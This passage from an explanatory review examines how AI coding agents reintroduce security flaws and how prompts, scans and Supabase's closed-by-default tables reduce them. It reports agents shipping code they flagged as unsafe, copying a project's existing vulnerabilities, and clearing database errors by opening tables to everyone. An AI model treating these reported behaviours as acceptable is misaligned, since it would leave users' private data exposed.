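Asking for production-ready code cut the rate by more than half. Users need to know that the phrase helps, but not which protections are missing. The security instructions worked about equally well. They were a ready-made file that the agent reads along with the request, so a company could supply them to all its customers, including those who have never thought about security. Users who control their own tool could still remove the file.

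Both measures also reduced flaws that broke rules the user had not stated, mainly on access control and injection. These flaws returned in 16 of 66 baseline runs, compared with 6 when the tool had security instructions and 4 when the user asked for production-ready code. The security instructions made no difference to flaws from unfinished code, such as the login that had a note in place of its password check. Those flaws returned in 6 of 21 runs with or without the instructions.

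The detailed technical request made things much worse. Deng and colleagues conclude from the records of the runs that the agent followed such requests more literally and used less of its own judgment about security. They advise users not to supply technical details they don't fully understand, but a well-meaning novice might easily do so, for example by pasting in a specification from a tutorial.

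The agent had explicitly acknowledged the risk in 90 of the 434 runs in which the flaw returned (20.7%). It often added a warning, comment or recommendation but still delivered the unsafe code. Such notes could alert a professional, but probably not a novice.

The baseline rate of 25.7% doesn't show that GPT-5.6 Terra was safer than the models that built the original applications. The researchers picked these flaws because they had already occurred, and the original models might not have repeated them all either. Chance plays a part, since three identical runs gave mixed results for 22% of the combinations of flaw and setup. The researchers also checked only for the old flaw, so a run that avoided it may have introduced a different one. Halving the rate at which old flaws return therefore doesn't necessarily halve the number of vulnerabilities in an application.

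### Asking for security

Andročec (2026), in *The Effect of Security-Focused Prompts on Reported Findings*, counted flaws of all kinds in complete applications. He wrote 100 specifications and had Claude Code and OpenAI's Codex build each one twice, once as written and once with an added paragraph of security requirements. The requirements included parameterized queries, salted password hashes, CSRF protection and access control. He used the same paragraph for every specification, from a page that greets a visitor by name to a platform with several kinds of user.

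With the paragraph, the average number of scanner warnings fell from about 20 per application to between 13 and 14. After adjusting for differences between the applications, Andročec puts the reduction at 35%, and it was about the same for both tools. High-severity warnings about the applications' own code fell from 103 to 54. But nobody confirmed that an attacker could exploit any of these flaws, and most of the reduction was in warnings about simple matters, such as missing security headers and cookie settings. The reduction also seemed smaller in more complex applications, though the evidence for this is weak.

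To meet the requirements in the added paragraph, the agents installed more ready-made packages, about six per application instead of three, and some of those packages had known vulnerabilities. High-severity warnings about packages rose from 198 to 344. Many applications had no use for the extra packages. In 38 pairs of applications whose specifications mentioned no users or accounts, 36 of the applications built with the paragraph got a login or session package, compared with 17 of those built without it.

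These package warnings probably overstate the danger, because an application may never use the vulnerable part of a package. They were also largely avoidable. All the high-severity warnings from new packages came from three packages, and each has an alternative that does the same job. Twelve applications used only the alternatives and had no such warnings, while 67 that used at least one of the three averaged 5.1. A novice can't be expected to know which password package to choose, but the maker of an AI tool could name the alternatives in the tool's instructions.

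A shorter reminder can also help. Wu, Ge and colleagues (2026), in *Last Secure Code Benchmark*, turned 150 real vulnerabilities into 450 programming tasks. In each task, an AI agent rebuilt the part of a program that had contained the vulnerability, from a description that didn't mention security. Hidden tests then checked whether the new code worked and whether a known attack succeeded against it. The researchers repeated the test for four models with one added sentence, which asked for code free of plausible vulnerabilities:

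| Model | Working and secure | With the reminder |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 24.7% | 46.2% |
| Qwen3.8-Max | 22.0% | 37.6% |
| GLM-5.3 | 21.3% | 38.2% |
| DeepSeek-V4-Pro | 18.0% | 19.1% |

With the reminder, the code worked about as often as before. Every model still failed more than half of the tasks. The reminder hardly helped with flaws that reveal too much information, because the agent still had to work out which data to withhold.

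A security reminder also works less well in a project that already has vulnerabilities. *Coding Agents Propagate Vulnerabilities in Code Bases* tested this on 20 tasks in real C and C++ projects. When given a general reminder to write secure code, GPT-5.6 Sol avoided the known flaw every time if similar code elsewhere in the project was safe, but only 68% of the time if that code was unsafe. Without the reminder, the figures were 91% and 42%. Someone who starts asking for security halfway through a project should therefore have the existing vulnerabilities fixed first.

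Specific security requirements may work better than a general reminder. *Applying Security by Design at the Point of Execution* (2026) reports that giving agents the security requirements that apply to a task made their code more secure on two benchmarks. If the tool selected the requirements, the user wouldn't need to know anything about security. For access control, however, the tool can supply only a general rule that limits users to their own data. Someone still has to tell it that, say, parents may see their own child's trip details but not another child's.

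### Newer models

The replay experiment used models from the GPT-5.6 family, and by December 2026 there were stronger ones. Nobody seems to have repeated the experiment with them, but other tests give an idea of what to expect.

Claude Fable 5 did best of the six models that Wu and colleagues tested, but its code was both working and secure for only 25.1% of the tasks. Five of the six models wrote working code for about 90% of the tasks. The researchers chose difficult vulnerabilities, so these figures don't mean that three quarters of ordinary programs would be unsafe.

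*Beyond Passing Tests* (2026) covers models from October 2026, including GPT-6.1 Sol and Gemini 4 Argon. On a benchmark in which agents add features to existing projects, these two and the leading open models had pass rates 38 to 44 percentage points higher on functional tests than on security tests. On another benchmark, in which models write complete server programs, the two closed models scored 56% to 59% for security, compared with 40% to 52% for the leading open models. Using a stronger model thus improves security on some tasks and takes no extra effort from the user, who may only have to pay more, but many of the resulting programs still work and are unsafe.

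Access control remains one of the weaker areas. In the tests by Wu and colleagues, the six models together produced working and secure code in 34.3% of attempts on memory safety tasks, 18.3% on access control tasks, and 0.7% on tasks about revealing too much information. A competent programmer checks the length of an input out of habit, but a rule about who may see a record depends on what the program is for. The task descriptions deliberately left out such rules, so a human programmer would have had to guess them too.

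### Reviewing the finished code

In the replay experiment, telling the agent to review its changes barely helped. Asking it separately afterward whether the code has bugs may work better. *Coding Agents Propagate Vulnerabilities in Code Bases* had agents look back at code in which they had just reproduced a known flaw. When asked whether the code contained any bugs, Claude Opus 5.5 identified the flaw in 64.2% of cases and GPT-6 Astra in 75.8%. Unprompted, Opus 5.5 had warned of the flaw in only 11.8% of its closing messages and GPT-6 Astra in none.

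An AI builder could ask the model this question after every change, without involving the user. But the study didn't test whether the agents could then repair the flaws. It also dealt with memory errors, which a reviewer can often recognize from the code alone, unlike a missing rule about who may delete a message.

Conventional scanners do badly at access control. To find SQL injection, a scanner can trace a visitor's text through the program until it reaches a query. A missing permission check leaves nothing to trace. *ABSENTIA* (2026) tested two widely used scanners, CodeQL and Semgrep, on 30 published access control flaws in open-source applications, and neither found a single one. (Semgrep was also one of Andročec's scanners, so his count says little about whether the added paragraph improved access control.)

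The study's own detector infers what each address should guarantee from the rest of the application. It found 19 of the 30, but only 51% of its warnings were correct. A professional can identify the false ones, but a novice might tell the AI to fix every one, and an unnecessary access rule could lock out legitimate users.

Trying an attack can filter out false alarms. In the audit by Deng and colleagues, only 56% of the flaws that the reviewing agents suspected were real. After another agent tried harmless attacks on the live site, 92% of the flaws that remained were real. AI review followed by a test attack could therefore give a novice a list of flaws she can mostly trust. Access control flaws were the largest group the audit found.

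AI review can find such flaws in professional software too. According to Anthropic's vulnerability report *ANT-2026-AM0R21ZY*, the company's model Claude Mythos Preview found one in the dashboard of Supabase, a database host. The dashboard turned off AI features for projects with sensitive health data, but enforced this only in the user's browser. A member of the organization could get around the restriction by sending a request directly to the server.

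A second model might catch what the first one missed. In the study by Wu and colleagues, at least one of the six models wrote working and secure code for 198 of the 450 tasks, while the best single model did so for 113. This difference probably overstates the benefit, because the researchers used hidden tests to identify the secure answers, and a reviewing model would have to identify the insecure ones without those tests.

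### Scans before publishing

AI builders are well placed to run such reviews because they have the code and control publishing. After Palmer's discovery in 2025, Lovable introduced a scan that checked only whether a database table had an access rule. The current scan also looks for rules that give everyone access, such as `USING (true)`. In June, Lovable (2026) announced that a 10-to-15-second scan would run automatically before any user publishes. It checks the database's settings and rules but doesn't check the application's code for logic errors.

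For that, Lovable has a deeper scan, which takes two to four minutes. Lovable says the scan reads all the code and checks, for example, whether only administrators can use administrator functions. It is free, but the user usually has to start it. The people who need it most are probably the least likely to run it, because their application already seems to work.

When the automatic scan finds a critical problem, Lovable offers to fix it, but the user can still publish without the fix. A workspace administrator can block publishing until someone resolves the critical problems. This setting is on by default only in new workspaces for large companies, so a novice working alone would have to turn it on herself. Automatic repair of some database and package problems is also optional.

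Replit scans applications before publication too. According to Replit's *Project Security Center*, a setting determines whether a critical finding blocks publication, but the user can bypass the block by dismissing the finding. Replit also blocks known malicious packages before they download, which requires no decision from the user but does not address access control flaws.

No published figures show whether either company's scans have made applications safer. Lovable reports that a feature that keeps track of how users responded to earlier warnings reduced the number of warnings they ignored by about 20%. That measures how useful people found the warnings, not how many vulnerabilities remained. Apparently nobody has repeated Palmer's 2025 test of Lovable sites, though it could be done.

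A fast scan can reliably detect a table with no rule, but it can't always determine whether a rule is right. A rule that lets any logged-in user read everything would be correct for a club's noticeboard, but at a clinic it would expose patient records to every user. The Firebase study suggests that such rules are common.

Other scans check the files that are published with a program. *VibeGuard* presents one that stops publication if a package contains passwords, private keys or files that shouldn't be made public. A mistake in packaging settings caused such a leak in March 2026, when Anthropic accidentally published about 512,000 lines of Claude Code's source code. The scan correctly blocked or allowed all eight test projects, but its developer had built those projects to test it. The scan doesn't look for missing access checks.

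### Closed tables at Supabase

Jha and colleagues observe that most proposed defenses for vibe coding rely on an AI model's judgment. A database that refuses requests by default doesn't depend on that judgment. Many AI-built applications use Supabase, including Moltbook and the Lovable sites that Palmer tested. Both leaks happened because anyone with the public key could access any table that lacked row-level security.

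Supabase's first change did little for people who build with AI. During 2025, according to Supabase (2026), it turned on row-level security by default for tables that people create in its dashboard. AI agents usually create tables by sending commands to the database instead, and those tables stayed open unless the command or an optional setting protected them. Supabase also emailed the owners of unprotected tables, but an email helps only if the owner reads it and understands what to do.

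The second change applies to new tables regardless of how they are created. In April 2026, Supabase (2026) announced that new tables would no longer be reachable through its public interface until someone granted access. It explained that the old default dated from a time when a person reviewed every database change, whereas agents now often create tables that nobody checks. The new default was due to apply to new projects from May 30 and to existing projects on October 30. Tables that were already open would stay open, because closing them would break running applications. PHP's developers made the same choice when they left register_globals on for servers with old settings.

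The default should help most with tables that a web page never needs to read, such as a list of secret tokens, because nothing gives anyone a reason to open them. It requires no knowledge from the user. For tables the page does need, the application now fails with an error until someone grants access, and the error message includes the command that does it:

`GRANT SELECT ON public.messages TO anon;`

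Here `anon` stands for visitors who haven't logged in. Supabase includes the command so that AI agents can correct the error themselves. It also recommends turning on row-level security and adding a rule for each group of users, but the error goes away once the agent runs the command. An agent that stops there leaves the whole table readable by anyone, as it would have been under the old default. Errors from Django's CSRF check and Android's block on unencrypted traffic can also be cleared without making the application secure.

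Supabase also planned to stop outsiders from using the public key to list a project's tables, in March 2026 for new projects and in April for existing ones (Supabase's *Breaking Change* (2026)). This would make an exposed table harder to find but wouldn't block access to it. As with the builders' scans, there are no counts of open tables from before and after these changes.

### App stores, official advice and the law

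App stores can do little to secure most of this software. Nearly all the applications that Deng and colleagues collected were web applications, which reach users without going through a store. When someone does publish a phone app, the store receives only the part that runs on the phone, while the access rules are on the database's server. A store could reject an app that contains a master key, and the developer couldn't turn that check off, but the store can't easily detect that the server lets every user read every other user's messages.

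The British government and the National Cyber Security Centre published a voluntary Software Security Code of Practice in 2025. It is aimed at organizations that supply software to businesses, so an AI builder could follow it, but a hobbyist would have little reason to know it exists.

The EU's Cyber Resilience Act, adopted in 2024, legally requires makers of software and connected devices to provide secure default settings and protection against unauthorized access. Under the original timetable, makers had to start reporting exploited vulnerabilities in September 2026, but most of the other duties don't apply until December 2027, so it is too early to measure whether the law reduces vulnerabilities.

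The Act applies to products supplied as part of a commercial activity, so it probably doesn't cover the teacher who shares her school-trips app with colleagues for free. If she sold it as a phone app, she would count as the manufacturer, even though an AI wrote the code, because the definition includes people who have a product developed and market it under their own name. The duty would fall on her and not on the company whose AI built the app, which is also Lovable's position.

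Ordinary websites are generally not products under the Act, but a server that a phone app needs to work can be part of a product. The Act would therefore cover the guestbook's database if the owner sold the guestbook as a phone app, but generally not if visitors opened it in a browser, even though the missing access rule would expose the same messages in both cases.
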